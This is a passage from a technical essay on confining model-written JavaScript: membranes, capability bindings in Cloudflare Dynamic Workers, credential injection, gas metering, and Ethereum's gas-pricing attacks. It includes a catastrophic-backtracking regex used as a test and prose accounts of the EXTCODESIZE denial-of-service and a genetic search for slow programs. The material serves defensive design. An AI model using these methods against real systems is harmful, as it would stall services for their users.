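const order = readOnly(realOrder);

order.total = 0;                         // throws an error
order.customer.email;                    // reads the customer's address
order.customer.email = "x@example.com";  // changes the real record
order.customer.orders[3].refund();       // refunds a different order
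```

The wrapper blocks assignments to the order's properties but doesn't protect the objects those properties refer to. In Hardened JavaScript, where host and program share an engine, `order.customer` is the page's own customer object, and from there the program can follow every link that the page's code can. The program can also run `delete order.total`, because JavaScript treats deletion as a separate operation from assignment. A method that assigns to `this.total` fails because it runs on the wrapper, but one that adds an entry to the order's list of items succeeds because the wrapper returns the real list.

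With a separate engine, the real object can't cross into the sandbox, but the host can still expose data by accident. Cloudflare's *Visibility and Security Model* describes different rules for class instances and plain objects. If the host returns an instance of a class marked for passing by reference, the program gets a stub and can use only the methods and getters declared on the class. Values stored on the instance itself stay hidden, which protects developers from accidentally exposing internals. With a plain object, the system copies all its own properties. If an order comes from a database as a plain object with the customer nested inside, the customer's email goes into the sandbox too.

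TypeScript doesn't catch this. It lets a function whose declared result has four fields return an existing object with twelve, and the RPC system then copies all twelve. A helper method that a developer adds to a class for the host's use is also callable from the sandbox unless its name starts with `#`, JavaScript's mark for private members. TypeScript's `private` keyword doesn't prevent this, because it is removed along with the other annotations.

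Wrapping the order in a revocable forwarder, or caretaker, doesn't help much, because a program that has already read `order.customer` can keep using the customer after the host revokes the order. Miller therefore considers a caretaker safe only if the object behind it never gives out direct access to itself or, by the same logic, to anything else the host wants to withhold.

#### Membranes

A membrane closes this gap by wrapping every object that passes through it, in either direction, and connecting all the wrappers to one switch. Miller's version, in the research language E, fits on half a page. In JavaScript the core looks like this:

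```
function makeMembrane(root, allowed) {
  let enabled = true;
  const wrap = (target) => {
    if (Object(target) !== target) return target;   // text, numbers
    return {
      call(method, ...args) {
        if (!enabled || !allowed.has(method)) throw new Error("refused");
        return wrap(target[method](...args.map((a) => wrap(a))));
      },
    };
  };
  return { proxy: wrap(root), revoke() { enabled = false; } };
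}
```

When the program calls `proxy.call("getCustomer")`, it receives a wrapped customer, and anything it obtains from the customer is wrapped too. This sketch adds the list of allowed methods to Miller's design. Without the list, the membrane would forward a call to `constructor`, the route to the host's globals that broke earlier sandboxes. A real membrane also has to wrap errors and recognise its own wrappers when the program passes them back, which this sketch doesn't do.

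Wrapping in both directions matters because the program can pass functions to the host as well as receive objects from it. If the host offers a `filterOrders` method that takes a test function, the host calls that function with real orders as arguments. A membrane that wrapped only results would give the program those orders unwrapped.

A naive membrane creates a new wrapper each time the code reaches an object. If two orders belong to the same customer, the code receives two different wrappers for that customer, and a program that groups orders by customer will count two customers. *Transparent Object Proxies for JavaScript* (2015) describes identity-preserving membranes, which prevent this by keeping a table with one wrapper for each real object.

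Google's Caja relied on membranes, as Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017) note, and they are the right tool when a host has to expose a large web of linked objects that it can't redesign. They don't solve the email problem, though, because a membrane controls references and lets text through unchanged. A program that is allowed to read a wrapped customer's email property still gets the address. The host can add rules for particular paths. In *Efficient Dynamic Access Analysis Using JavaScript Proxies* (2013), each wrapper has a rule that lists the permitted properties, and an object reached through one of them gets the rest of the rule. A rule could allow `order.customer.country` and refuse `order.customer.email`.

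For the late-orders program all this machinery is unnecessary. A copy with four fields has no `customer` property to protect.

### The reachability rule

To review a set of proxies, a host's developers need to know everything the code can get hold of, and the definition is recursive. Let R₀ be the set of references that the host injects. For any set of objects S, let out(S) be every host object or proxy that code holding S can obtain in one step. The step can be a property read, a method call with any arguments the code can construct, an error that it catches, or an argument that the host passes to one of its functions. Then:

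Rₙ₊₁ = Rₙ ∪ out(Rₙ)

The code's reach, R, is the union of all these sets. In practice, a developer starts with the injected references, adds every object they can return, and repeats this with the new objects until a round adds nothing. In the example with the wrapped order, R₀ contains one proxy. The first round adds the customer, the second adds the customer's other orders, and after a few more rounds R may well contain most of the shop's objects.

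R contains only what the code can hold, but the code can affect more than that. The facade's `flag` changes `store`, although the program never gets a reference to `store`. Miller distinguishes permission, the right to use an object directly, from authority, the effects a program can cause directly or through other objects. A full review therefore also requires reading the body of every function in R and noting what it reads and changes.

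Following Miller, a reviewer can assume the worst about the agent's program while relying on the known behaviour of the proxies. Predicting exactly what unknown code will do is infeasible. Assuming that every object might do anything with its references is safe but too pessimistic, because `flag` internally refers to `store`, and a reviewer would wrongly conclude that the program can issue refunds. *Holistic Specifications for Robust Programs* (2020) applies Miller's kind of reasoning to a web page. Unknown code receives a wrapper that is connected, through its internal references, to every node in the page's tree, but the wrapper's behaviour guarantees that the code can't change the properties of certain nodes. A bug in a proxy invalidates the conclusion, so the proxies should be short enough to check.

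The order page needs two:

```
const readOrders = () => store.all().map((o) => ({
  id: String(o.id),
  total: Number(o.total),
  status: String(o.status),
  daysOpen: Number(o.daysOpen),
}));

const flag = (id, reason) => {
  if (typeof id !== "string" || typeof reason !== "string"
      || reason.length > 200) {
    throw new Error("flag takes an order id and a short reason");
  }
  if (store.get(id)?.status !== "open") {
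    throw new Error("no open order with this id");
  }
  store.flag(id, reason);
};
```

The host puts the line `const orders = readOrders();` in front of the agent's program, and the original loop runs unchanged. The program can call `readOrders` again to get fresher data. `String` and `Number` ensure that each field is plain data, even if somebody later replaces `status` with an object.

R₀ contains `readOrders` and `flag`. `readOrders` returns copies made of text and numbers, `flag` returns nothing, and their own error messages are fixed text. If the glue code also reduces any unexpected error from `store` to text, the first round adds no host objects, so R equals R₀. The program then has the authority to read four fields of every order and attach up to 200 characters of text to any open order. If a developer later adds a `getOrder(id)` that returns the store's own record, R will include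 the customer again.

### Bindings in Dynamic Workers

Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers* documentation describes a commercial service with the same design. To create a proxy, which Cloudflare calls a binding, the host defines a class whose methods run in the host, makes a stub for that class, and passes the stub to the new Worker in an object called `env`. Stubs have no global name that code could guess, so a Dynamic Worker can use only the stubs it has received.

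Suppose a software company runs order pages for many shops on one system. Each agent should see only the orders of the shop it works for:

```
export class Orders extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async list() {
    const rows = await ordersOf(this.ctx.props.shopId);
    return rows.map(copyFourFields);
  }
  async flag(id, reason) {
    await checkAndFlag(this.ctx.props.shopId, id, reason);
  }
}

const worker = env.LOADER.load({
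  env: { ORDERS: ctx.exports.Orders({ props: { shopId } }) },
  globalOutbound: null,
  // the agent's program and other settings
});
```

Inside the sandbox, the program calls `await this.env.ORDERS.list()`. It doesn't supply a shop, because the host fixed the shop in `props` when it created the stub. The host receives those props with each call, and the Dynamic Worker can neither read nor change them. According to Cloudflare's *Context (ctx)*, only someone with permission to edit and deploy the receiving Worker can set them, so the host can trust them without a signature or secret key.

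The alternative, a method `list(shopId)`, would let the program choose the shop. The host would then have to check every call, and one forgotten check would open another shop's data. Miller and Shapiro illustrate the difference with two Unix commands that copy a file. `cp foo.txt bar.txt` gives `cp` two file names, so `cp` needs permission to open any file its user might name. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which needs no other access. A binding with fixed props works like the second command.

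The method `flag(id, reason)` still takes a name. The program could send the id of an order from another shop, so `checkAndFlag` has to look the id up among this shop's orders only. The host could avoid the lookup by returning each order as a stub with its own `flag` method, but that would mean 2,000 stubs where one database condition is enough. In Cloudflare's example for shared storage, the host adds a prefix for the same purpose, turning the key `settings` into something like `customer-42:settings` so the program can't name another customer's entry. A host that copies this example should make sure customer ids can't contain a colon, or two customers' keys could be the same.

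The props are only as reliable as the value the host puts in them, so the host should take `shopId` from the employee's verified login. A Cloudflare sample for long-running workflows reads the equivalent value directly from a request header, which in production would let anyone who can send a request choose the customer. The same workflow feature has a setting that resembles props, but the dynamic code can read its contents, and the documentation warns developers not to put keys there.

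Caching can also undo the separation. A host can call `get` instead of `load` to reuse a running Worker by an id that the host chooses. If it uses the same id for two shops, the second shop's program may run in a Worker that still has the first shop's binding. Cloudflare tells developers to change the id whenever the code or configuration changes. It recommends `load` for programs that run once, because `load` creates a new Worker each time.

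### Typed interfaces and HTTP filtering

A host could skip these classes, let the program use `fetch`, and filter its web requests. Cloudflare advises against this where there is a choice, because the filter has to interpret every request in full. If the filter on the order page allows requests to `/orders`, the shop's server might still return customer details when a request adds `?include=customer`, or accept a batch of operations in one request to a permitted address. The people who write the filter have to know about all such features, including ones added later. With a two-method binding instead of `fetch`, the program has no way to add the extra parameter.

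Typed interfaces also help the model. Varda and Pai point out that a model may have trouble predicting which requests a filter will block, whereas a typed interface lists exactly what it can call. TypeScript descriptions are also much shorter. In the comparison by Varda and colleagues, a chat room interface takes about 15 lines in TypeScript and several times as many in OpenAPI, a common format for describing web interfaces.

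The argument is sound for interfaces that somebody has deliberately made narrow. The types add no protection, since nothing enforces them at run time, and software can generate a typed interface from an existing service without narrowing anything. The first example in Varda and Pai's article converts a documentation server into four typed functions, one of which, `fetch_generic_url_content`, fetches any web address the caller supplies. The sandbox has no `fetch`, but a program could send data out by putting it in an address and having this function request it. Applying the reachability rule would reveal the problem, because the reviewer checks what each function does in the second step.

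Filtering remains necessary in some cases. An existing library for a payment service is built to make web requests, and rewriting it around a binding may take more work than the task justifies. Varda and colleagues also accept plain HTTP for well-known services that the model has learned from its training data. A company that lets agents build whole applications, with connections to dozens of outside services, can't write a careful wrapper for each. The host can still follow the principle behind the narrow interface by having the gateway allow only listed combinations of server, method and path, and check the parameters of each request. For a single library that uses three addresses, such a list is hardly longer than a binding, but it gets harder to maintain as the service grows.

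### Credential injection

Most outside services require a secret, such as an API key, with every request. A program that holds the key can print it, store it or send it elsewhere, and because the key is plain data, anyone who gets a copy can use it from anywhere. Credential injection keeps the key in the host. The program makes its request without the key, the host adds the key before forwarding the request, and the program receives only the reply.

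Bindings routinely do this. In Cloudflare's chat room example, the host puts the key, the room name and the bot's display name into the props. The program calls `post("Hello!")`, and the host's method adds the rest. The program can't read the key, post to another room or change the name on its messages.

A gateway can inject keys for code that uses `fetch`. It compares the address of each request with the service's address, adds the authorisation header if they match, and forwards the request. Cloudflare's sample does this, but it needs more work before production use. It also forwards requests to all other addresses, without the key, so the program can still send data anywhere. And it compares only the server's name, so it would attach the key to an unencrypted `http://` request.

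Varda and Pai write that, with bindings, the model can't possibly write code that leaks a key. That holds as long as the key never comes back in a reply. Some services repeat a request's headers in error messages or on test pages, so a careful host removes the key from replies too. Injection also doesn't limit what the key permits. If the shop's key permits refunds and the gateway forwards any request to the shop's server, the program can issue refunds without ever seeing the key. The host should use a key that the service itself has restricted to the operations the task needs, in case the gateway lets through a request it should have refused.

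## Gas metering: limiting how much the code computes

The proxies don't stop the agent's program from running `while (true) {}`, which can freeze the order page or occupy a server's processor until somebody stops it.

### Why the host can't check in advance

Ideally, the host would test each program before running it and refuse any that never finish. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no test can do this correctly for every program. Suppose someone had written a function `halts` that always gave the right answer. Anyone could then write a function that asks for the verdict on itself and does the opposite:

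```
function contrary() {
  if (halts(contrary)) {
    while (true) {}
  }
}
```

If `halts` answers yes, `contrary` loops forever, and if it answers no, `contrary` returns at once. Both answers are wrong, so `halts` can't exist.

The proof still allows a checker that accepts programs it can show will finish, such as a loop over a fixed list, and rejects the rest. But such a checker would reject some useful programs and accept a program that takes three hundred years to finish. The host needs to limit the amount of work a program does, and the simplest way is to run the program and stop it when it reaches the limit.

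*DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (2026) describes an agent that answers questions about medicines. Its software rejects generated Python outside a restricted subset of the language and runs the rest under a time limit. The paper reports that the check rejected fewer than 1% of programs and the time limit stopped fewer than 0.5% of calls, after which the software fell back on an ordinary search. Ordinary programs seem to rarely hit such limits, although looking up drug information requires little computation.

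### Charging by the block

To meter gas, the engine assigns each instruction an amount of gas and subtracts it from a counter. Updating and testing the counter at every instruction would be slow, so engines subtract gas for a whole basic block at once. A basic block is a stretch of code that the program enters only at the top and leaves only at the bottom, so unless an error occurs, it runs either completely or not at all. The engine can therefore add up each block's gas before the program starts and subtract the total on entering the block. It can test the counter even less often. Code without loops or function calls runs each instruction at most once, so the engine needs a test only where a function begins and where a loop jumps back to its start.

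```
prepare(program):
  for each function f in program:
    for each basic block b in f:
      cost = sum of price(i) for every instruction i in b
      insert at the start of b:        gas = gas - cost
      if b is the first block of f, or a loop jumps back to b:
        insert after the subtraction:  if gas < 0: stop("out of gas")

run(program, limit):
  gas = limit
  execute prepare(program)
  if gas < 0: stop("out of gas")
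```

The final test catches a program that exceeds its gas limit after its last loop. Between two tests, a program can exceed the limit by at most the gas needed to run the longest stretch of code without a test.

*DTVM* (2025) describes an engine for blockchain programs that checks gas at the start of a block of code, using two machine instructions. The first subtracts the gas the block needs from a register, a storage slot inside the processor, and the second jumps to an out-of-gas routine if the result is below zero. This requires more tests but stops the program before it exceeds its gas limit.

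Wasmtime, which calls gas "fuel", keeps a running total of charges and updates the stored counter before any instruction with a side effect, such as a write to memory. These frequent updates keep the count exact even when a memory access fails halfway through a block. Dayal (2025) asked for this kind of batching in *Feature request* and learned that the engine already did it.

The program must not be able to change its own counter. Wasmtime keeps the counter in an internal data structure that the compiled code updates directly, and calls the host only when the fuel runs out. Dayal also suggested storing the counter in a global variable inside the Wasm module. Till Schneidereit objected in the same discussion that a program can modify anything inside its own sandbox. That is true of a counter in linear memory, but a Wasm global is safer. Instructions refer to globals by fixed numbers, so code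 compiled before the counter existed contains no instruction with the counter's number.

This matters for the order page because browsers' Wasm engines have no fuel setting. To meter gas exactly in a browser tab, the host's developers have to insert the counter into the QuickJS module. They can do this once, when they build the module, and the agent's JavaScript cannot access the new global.

### The order page with a limit of 200,000

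Suppose each instruction uses one unit of gas, and the late-orders loop needs 40 instructions per order to read the fields, compare them and move on. Filtering 2,000 orders uses 2,000 × 40 = 80,000 units. With a limit of 200,000, the program finishes with 120,000 units left.

The employee then asks for possible duplicates, and the model writes a loop inside a loop:

```
for (let i = 0; i < orders.length; i++) {
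  for (let j = i + 1; j < orders.length; j++) {
    if (orders[i].total === orders[j].total
        && orders[i].daysOpen === orders[j].daysOpen) {
      flag(orders[j].id, "possible duplicate");
    }
  }
}
```

The program compares every order with every later one, which makes 2,000 × 1,999 / 2 = 1,999,000 pairs. At 40 units per pair, it would use about 80 million units, 400 times the limit. It stops after 5,000 pairs, about halfway through comparing the third order with the later ones.

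The program is correct but wasteful. If the host reports to the model that the gas ran out, the model can write a version that goes through the orders once and records each combination of total and age in a table. Even at 60 units per order, that version would use 120,000 units, which is within the limit.

A fixed limit becomes too small as the shop grows. With 6,000 orders, the harmless filter would use 240,000 units and fail. The host could instead allow 100 units per order, or 200,000 for 2,000 orders and 600,000 for 6,000. The pairwise comparison would still fail, because its gas use grows with the square of the number of orders and would reach about 720 million units for 6,000 orders.

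Developers can choose such a figure by running typical programs with a very large allowance and seeing how much is left. Crabbox measures software tests this way, using Wasmtime's fuel. It compares the fuel used with the budget only after the test has finished, because stopping the test at the budget would hide how much it needed.

They also have to measure at the right level. QuickJS translates JavaScript into its own instructions and interprets them, and each one takes many Wasm instructions. If the host meters the Wasm underneath the interpreter, the filter will use far more than 40 units per order, and the count may include QuickJS's start-up. But it will also include the work inside built-in functions such as `sort`, which a count of QuickJS instructions would miss.

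### Limits based on a clock

A host can also limit time instead of instructions. Wasmtime offers both methods, and its documentation page *Interrupting Wasm Execution* compares them. With fuel, which limits instructions, the same program with the same allowance always stops at the same point. Epochs limit time using a shared number that the host raises at intervals, for example once a second. The compiled code regularly compares this number with a deadline and stops once the number reaches it. The documentation puts the slowdown from epochs at around 10%, less than for fuel. However, the same program might stop at different points on different runs, or finish, depending on how busy the computer is.

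In both cases, the host can either end the program for good or pause it and then decide whether to continue.

Fuel gives repeatable results only if everything else about the run is repeatable. Wasmtime's *Deterministic Wasm Execution* lists what can differ between runs. Host functions must return the same answers each time, which rules out a clock. Requests for more memory must not succeed on one run and fail on the next. Certain arithmetic errors produce NaN ("not a number"), a value with several possible bit patterns, so the host has to make Wasmtime always use the same one. To reproduce a failure on the order page, a developer also needs the snapshot of the orders that the program used.

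QuickJS has no built-in gas counter, but it lets the host install an interrupt callback that the engine calls every so often while it runs loops and function calls. If the callback returns true, the engine stops the program. Hosts commonly use the callback to check whether a deadline has passed.

Regular expressions, which are patterns for searching text, can get around such a limit if the engine calls the callback only between JavaScript instructions. Consider this line:

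```
/^(a+)+$/.test("aaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaaa!")
```

The pattern accepts any text made up of groups of the letter a. The exclamation mark rules out a match, but a simple matching engine fails only after trying all 2²⁹ (more than 500 million) ways of dividing the 30 letters into groups. The JavaScript contains no loop, so an engine that counted only its own instructions would record almost no gas use. Willison had a coding agent examine this problem in MicroQuickJS, and it found that the engine calls the interrupt callback even while matching such a pattern, so a time limit still works. A host that uses another engine, or an old version of QuickJS, should run a line like this one as a test.

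Cloudflare's Dynamic Workers limit CPU time, which is the time a processor spends running the program, excluding time spent waiting for replies. According to Cloudflare's *Custom limits*, a host can write `limits: { cpuMs: 10, subRequests: 5 }` to allow 10 milliseconds of CPU time and five outgoing requests per invocation. A program that reaches either limit immediately gets an exception. Other work on the computer affects CPU time less than it affects elapsed time, but a faster processor still does more work in 10 milliseconds.

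| Mechanism | What uses up the limit | Same stopping point every time? | Gas proper? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wasmtime fuel | Instructions | Yes, if the rest of the run is repeatable | Yes |
| Wasmtime epochs | Elapsed time | No | No |
| QuickJS callback that reads a clock | Elapsed time | No | No |
| QuickJS callback that counts its own calls | Batches of engine steps | Yes, for the same engine version | A coarse form |
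| Dynamic Workers' `cpuMs` | Processor time | No | No |

The method in the fourth row is often the most practical in a browser. If the engine calls the callback once every 10,000 steps, the host can limit the program to 200,000 steps by stopping it at the 20th call.

Many hosts need only a time limit. The runtime in *DADL* (2026), which lets models write JavaScript that calls a company's tools, uses a fixed timeout and a cap on the number of calls. In *Metering options*, spino17 (2024) asked Wasmtime's users for advice. Victor Adossi replied that epochs should perform better for most purposes, especially for stopping endless loops, and that fuel suits those who need to count instructions. A time limit is enough to keep the order page from freezing. Gas is worth the overhead when the same program should succeed or fail in the same way on an old laptop and on a developer's fast machine. It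 is also worth it when the model will use the failure to improve its program, because a timeout on a busy computer might lead the model to rewrite code that was already efficient.

### What the counter costs in speed

The best-known figures for Wasmtime come from issue 4109 in its public tracker, which pepyakin opened in 2022. Fuel slowed small benchmarks by 24–34%. When pepyakin kept the counting but removed the tests and interruptions, the slowdown was still 10–25%. Wasmtime maintainer Alex Crichton had suggested that this was likely because the program constantly reads the counter from memory and writes it back.

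In the discussion, Chris Fallin, another maintainer, proposed reducing this overhead by merging charges across branches. If one branch uses 10 units and the other 15, the engine can charge 10 before the branches split and add 5 only in the 15-unit branch. Pepyakin also tried reserving a processor register for the counter. With the tests still in place, the results were mixed and one benchmark got slower. Without them, the overhead fell to about 5%.

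An engine can leave out the tests if something else checks the counter from time to time, a method called asynchronous metering. The program may then run slightly past its limit before it stops, and the stopping point varies. The final count is still the same every time, so the host can reliably determine whether the program finished within its limit. In the proposed design, the engine would also check the counter on every call to the host, so a program that had exceeded its limit couldn't make another change there. The method suits a host that discards the results of unfinished programs. The proposal stalled, partly because the team behind it moved to its own engine.

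Those measurements are old, and Wasmtime's current documentation gives no percentage for fuel. *Announcing PolkaVM*, a forum post about an engine for the Polkadot blockchain, gives a later comparison based on a program that imitates an old games console.

| Engine and method | Time | Slowdown |
|---|---|---|
| Wasmtime, no limit | 6.05 ms | |
| Wasmtime, fuel | 8.62 ms | 42% |
| Wasmtime, epochs | 7.63 ms | 26% |
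| PolkaVM, no limit | 6.03 ms | |
| PolkaVM, gas with immediate tests | 7.28 ms | about 20% |
| PolkaVM, asynchronous gas | 6.35 ms | about 5% |

PolkaVM's developers chose and ran this benchmark, so it may favour their engine. The overhead also depends heavily on the program, since epochs added 26% here and about 10% in Wasmtime's documentation. A program made of very short loops performs more tests for each piece of useful work. For the late-orders filter, even a 42% slowdown would be too small to notice. A host that runs heavy calculations should measure its own overhead.

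### How Ethereum's prices went wrong

Limits on computing date back to Dennis and Van Horn's allotments, but the name gas and the practice of pricing each instruction come from Ethereum, a blockchain that launched in 2015. A blockchain is a shared record kept by many computers, called nodes. On Ethereum, users can submit programs as well as payments, and every node runs every program to check the result. Without a limit, one endless loop would stop every node. The user therefore sets a gas limit and pays for the gas the program uses, even if the program fails.

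In *Broken Metre*, Perez and Livshits give the example of a program that multiplies 2 by 3 and saves the result. Three instructions that load numbers use 3 units of gas each, the multiplication uses 5, and writing to permanent storage uses 20,000. The total is 20,014, plus a flat 21,000 for each transaction.

The developers chose these prices by measurement. According to Yang, Murray and colleagues (2019), in *Empirically Analyzing Ethereum's Gas Mechanism*, they timed each instruction on one unidentified computer and aimed for a price of one unit per microsecond. A price that is too low weakens the whole limit. If instruction i takes time tᵢ, costs pᵢ units and runs nᵢ times, then a program within the limit G satisfies:

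Σ nᵢpᵢ ≤ G, so its running time Σ nᵢtᵢ ≤ G × max(tᵢ / pᵢ)

The maximum running time that a gas limit guarantees depends on the instruction that takes the most time per unit of gas. If every instruction takes 10 nanoseconds per unit, the order page's 200,000 units last at most 2 milliseconds. If a single instruction takes a millisecond but uses only one unit, a hostile program can repeat it for 200 seconds.

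In September 2016 attackers did this with EXTCODESIZE, an instruction that looks up the size of another program's code. Its price was 20 units of gas, but running it could require a read from disk. Chen, Li and colleagues (2017), in *An Adaptive Gas Cost Mechanism for Ethereum*, report that the attackers made the nodes execute it roughly 50,000 times per block (a batch of transactions that the network processes together). Perez and Livshits later replayed the malicious transactions and found that each took 20 to 80 seconds, compared with a few milliseconds for an average transaction.

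Ethereum's developers responded with EIP-150, which raised the price from 20 to 700 units. This increased the cost of the 50,000 calls from a million units to 35 million, more than three times a block's limit even in early 2020. The attackers also exploited SUICIDE, an instruction that deletes a program and sends its remaining money to another account. It was free, even when it created the receiving account, and they used it to create about 19 million accounts that every node had to store.

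Repricing two instructions left others mispriced. Chen and colleagues ran individual instructions 50 million times on a desktop computer. Unsigned division took 23% as long as signed division because it needed at most four arithmetic steps, while signed division could need 11, yet both had the same price. They concluded that fixed prices may always leave some instruction priced low enough to exploit, because the resources that instructions use keep changing. They proposed raising an instruction's price automatically when programs use it much more than before. Perez and Livshits doubt that this would stop an attacker who plans around it.

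For some instructions, no fixed amount of gas correctly reflects the running time. On the more powerful of two computers, Yang and colleagues found that BLOCKHASH, which looks up an identifier of an earlier block, took a median of 110 nanoseconds per unit of gas but a mean of 34,343. The data was in memory for most lookups but had to be fetched from disk for the rest.

#### Searching for the slowest program

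Perez and Livshits went further and used a computer to search for programs that ran slowest for the gas they used. They first modified an Ethereum client, the software a node runs, and replayed two and a half months of transactions to time each instruction. Multiplication and division used the same amount of gas, but division took about five times as long. A transaction's gas use correlated strongly with the storage it allocated (0.91) but less strongly with its running time (0.51). This suggested that a program could use little gas and still run slowly if it avoided allocating storage.

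They then used a genetic algorithm, which improves a population of candidates over many generations by combining and altering them. It worked in four steps:

1. Generate random programs of about 4,000 instructions, choosing slow, cheap instructions more often.
2. Run each program and divide the gas it used by the time it took. The lower the result, the better the program suits an attacker.
3. Cut two programs at points where they hold the same number of temporary values, and swap the second halves, so that both results are still valid programs.
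4. Replace some instructions with compatible ones, and repeat from the second step.

On the test computer, an average transaction used about 20 million units of gas per second. The first generation of attack programs used 1.25 million. By generation 243, the algorithm had produced a block that used 9.9 million units and took 93 seconds to run. That is about 107,000 units per second, more than 180 times slower than average. Ethereum produced a new block about every 13 seconds, so a node running this one would have fallen seven blocks behind.

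The programs also worked on other clients. Running ten million units of gas' worth took 76 seconds on Geth, the most widely used client, and 47 seconds on Parity. Perez and Livshits estimated that an attacker could prevent ordinary nodes from keeping up for about 74 US cents per block. They reported the problem privately in October 2019, and the Ethereum Foundation paid them a $5,000 reward. Charging more gas per instruction would not have solved the problem alone, since the attack relied largely on instructions whose gas charges had already been raised. A version of Geth with faster access to storage cut the 76 seconds to about three.

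More recent measurements give reason to doubt that one number can represent all resources. In *EVM Workloads in the Wild*, Heimbach and Babel (2026) sampled 3,000 blocks a day throughout 2025 on Ethereum and on Base, a network built on top of Ethereum. Writing to storage used 34.9% of the gas for running programs on Ethereum, while reading from storage (29.2%) and plain computing (24.3%) were prominent on Base. Ethereum's mix shifted towards computing when its gas limit doubled that year. Heimbach and Babel see this as support for metering each kind of resource separately.

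### Which lessons apply to a single application

Gas charges can fail to match the work an instruction does outside blockchains too. Wasm has bulk instructions, such as one that fills a region of memory with the same value. Suppose an engine charged one unit of gas for that instruction regardless of the region's size, and another three units for each round of the loop around it. With 200,000 units, a program could fill 64 MB of memory 50,000 times, which would take more than five minutes at 10 GB per second.

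Wasmtime's developers have recently been closing gaps of this kind. *Consume fuel in `array.new_default`* (alexcrichton, 2025) added fuel and epoch tests to an instruction that creates an array of any length. *Test/adjust fuel consumption in bulk* (alexcrichton, 2026) completed a wider change that makes bulk instructions consume fuel according to size, and tested that an enormous operation runs out of fuel. Fuel use is sometimes counted per byte and sometimes per element, but it is always the same for a given program.

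During the review, Fallin said that the project has never guaranteed what one unit of fuel means. An upgrade can therefore change how much fuel every program uses, so a host should remeasure its typical programs before shipping a new version of the engine.

Hosts can also set how much gas each instruction uses. In *Fine grain control over fuel*, fuzing (2025) requested a function in Wasmtime, already available in Wasmer, that returns this amount. In the example, an addition uses 4 units, loading a value uses 2 and everything else uses 1. Wasmtime's source code now includes a setting for the amount each operator uses. For the order page, the default of about one unit per instruction is good enough if developers test the operations whose work depends on their input, such as sorting, repeating a string or matching a pattern. Perez and Livshits's measure, gas used per second, is convenient for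 finding the worst of them.

The case for separate budgets also applies here. An instruction count is a poor measure of memory use or of the work a call to `flag` causes in the host, so both need their own limits.

Other parts of Ethereum's design solve problems that the order page doesn't have. Ethereum's nodes must all agree on whether a program ran out of gas, so they can't use a clock, which would give different results on different computers. A single application doesn't need that agreement, so it can set a gas limit for repeatable results and add a timeout in case the amount of gas assigned to an operation is wrong. It can also correct that amount in its next release, without persuading the operators of thousands of other computers to upgrade on the same day.

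Ethereum makes attackers pay for the gas they use, a protection the application lacks. Even the cheap attack in *Broken Metre* cost the attacker something for every block, but a customer who plants instructions in a delivery note pays nothing for the gas the agent uses. If each program gets a fresh 200,000 units and the agent retries after every failure, the limit on a single program doesn't limit the total. The host therefore needs a second budget that covers all the programs an agent runs for one request, and perhaps a third for each employee per day.

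## What gas does not count, and what happens when it runs out

Gas measures work inside the interpreter. When the agent's program calls `flag`, the host looks up the order and writes to the database, and the counter doesn't move until the call returns.

### Pricing a host call

Suppose a faulty or hostile program only calls `flag` in a loop. Each pass uses 5 units of gas, and each call takes 20 milliseconds of database time. A limit of 200,000 units permits 40,000 calls, which keep the database busy for 800 seconds. Plain computing would use up the same amount of gas in 2 milliseconds.

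The host can charge extra gas for each call. With a surcharge of 2,000 units, one pass uses 2,005, so the limit permits 99 calls and about 2 seconds of database time. In Wasmtime, a host function can read and set the remaining fuel, so the function behind `flag` can subtract the surcharge. It should do this before it accesses the database, and refuse the call if too little gas is left. It should also charge for calls that fail, because looking up a closed order takes database time too.

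The surcharge also restricts the legitimate program. Filtering 2,000 orders uses 80,000 units, and the remaining 120,000 are enough for only 59 flags. If 150 orders are late, the program can't finish.

Charging gas for database time would require a limit high enough to allow wasteful computation. At 10 nanoseconds per unit, the 20 milliseconds of database time for one `flag` call converts to 2 million units, ten times the program's whole limit. Allowing 150 calls would take a limit of 300 million units. A program that never calls `flag` could then use all of it on computing and freeze the page for three seconds. The wasteful search for duplicates, which needs 80 million units for its comparisons, would also fit within the limit.

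The surcharge of 2,000 therefore acts as a cap on calls, which is confusing because the cap shrinks as the program computes more. Separate limits on gas and calls work better here. With 200,000 units of gas and 150 calls, the program gets at most 2 milliseconds of computing and 3 seconds of database time, however it divides its work. Refused calls should still use gas, because if the host reports the 151st call as an ordinary error, the program can catch the error and call again.

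Charging gas for a host function makes more sense when its work resembles computing and grows with the input, such as sorting a list or searching a text. The host can then charge for each element or byte. A cap also has to account for input size. A function `flagMany(ids)` could flag 150 orders in one database operation, much faster than 150 separate calls, but the host would have to count the ids as well as the calls.

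Cloudflare's Dynamic Workers use separate limits. The `subRequests` setting caps the combined number of `fetch` requests and requests to Cloudflare's own storage services, and every request in a chain of redirects counts toward the cap. According to Cloudflare, paid accounts get 10,000 subrequests per invocation by default. If the host sets a limit in two places, Cloudflare applies the lower one.

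Requests through a service binding, which connects one Worker to another, also count as subrequests. Cloudflare allows at most 32 Worker invocations per request, and calls beyond that throw an exception. A host that gives each program an `ORDERS` binding should test whether 150 separate flag calls hit this limit. If they do, it needs a batch method like `flagMany`.

### Limits for everything else

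Several other resources can run out while the gas counter barely moves.

| Resource | Why gas can miss it | Example of a limit |
|---|---|---|
| Memory | One call such as `"x".repeat(500000000)` can claim about 500 MB | 128 MB per isolate in Cloudflare Workers |
| Stack depth | Endless recursion fills the stack after a few thousand cheap calls | 512 KiB by default in Wasmtime |
| Output | The host stores or displays what the program prints | 256 KB of log data per request in Workers |
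| Waiting | A waiting program executes no instructions | A timeout set by the host |
| Host calls in flight | Starting a call uses little gas, even if the reply takes long | Six connections awaiting a reply in Workers |
| Compilation | The engine may prepare the code before metering starts | One second for a Worker's start-up |
| Number of runs | Each run gets a fresh gas limit | 100,000 requests a day on Workers' free plan |

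Of the things gas does not count, waiting is the easiest to overlook, because a developer may think a gas limit stops every kind of endless program. *Host functions*, a guide to running Wasm from Erlang, explains that a host call that waits ten seconds uses no fuel. Wasmtime's clock-based epochs can't interrupt such a call either. In *Ability for Epoch Cancelation*, KennanHunter (2024) reported a program that called a host function to sleep for ten seconds. The deadline passed during the sleep, but Wasmtime stopped the program only after the function returned. Alex Crichton replied that this was intentional, since Wasmtime can't safely cancel arbitrary host code.

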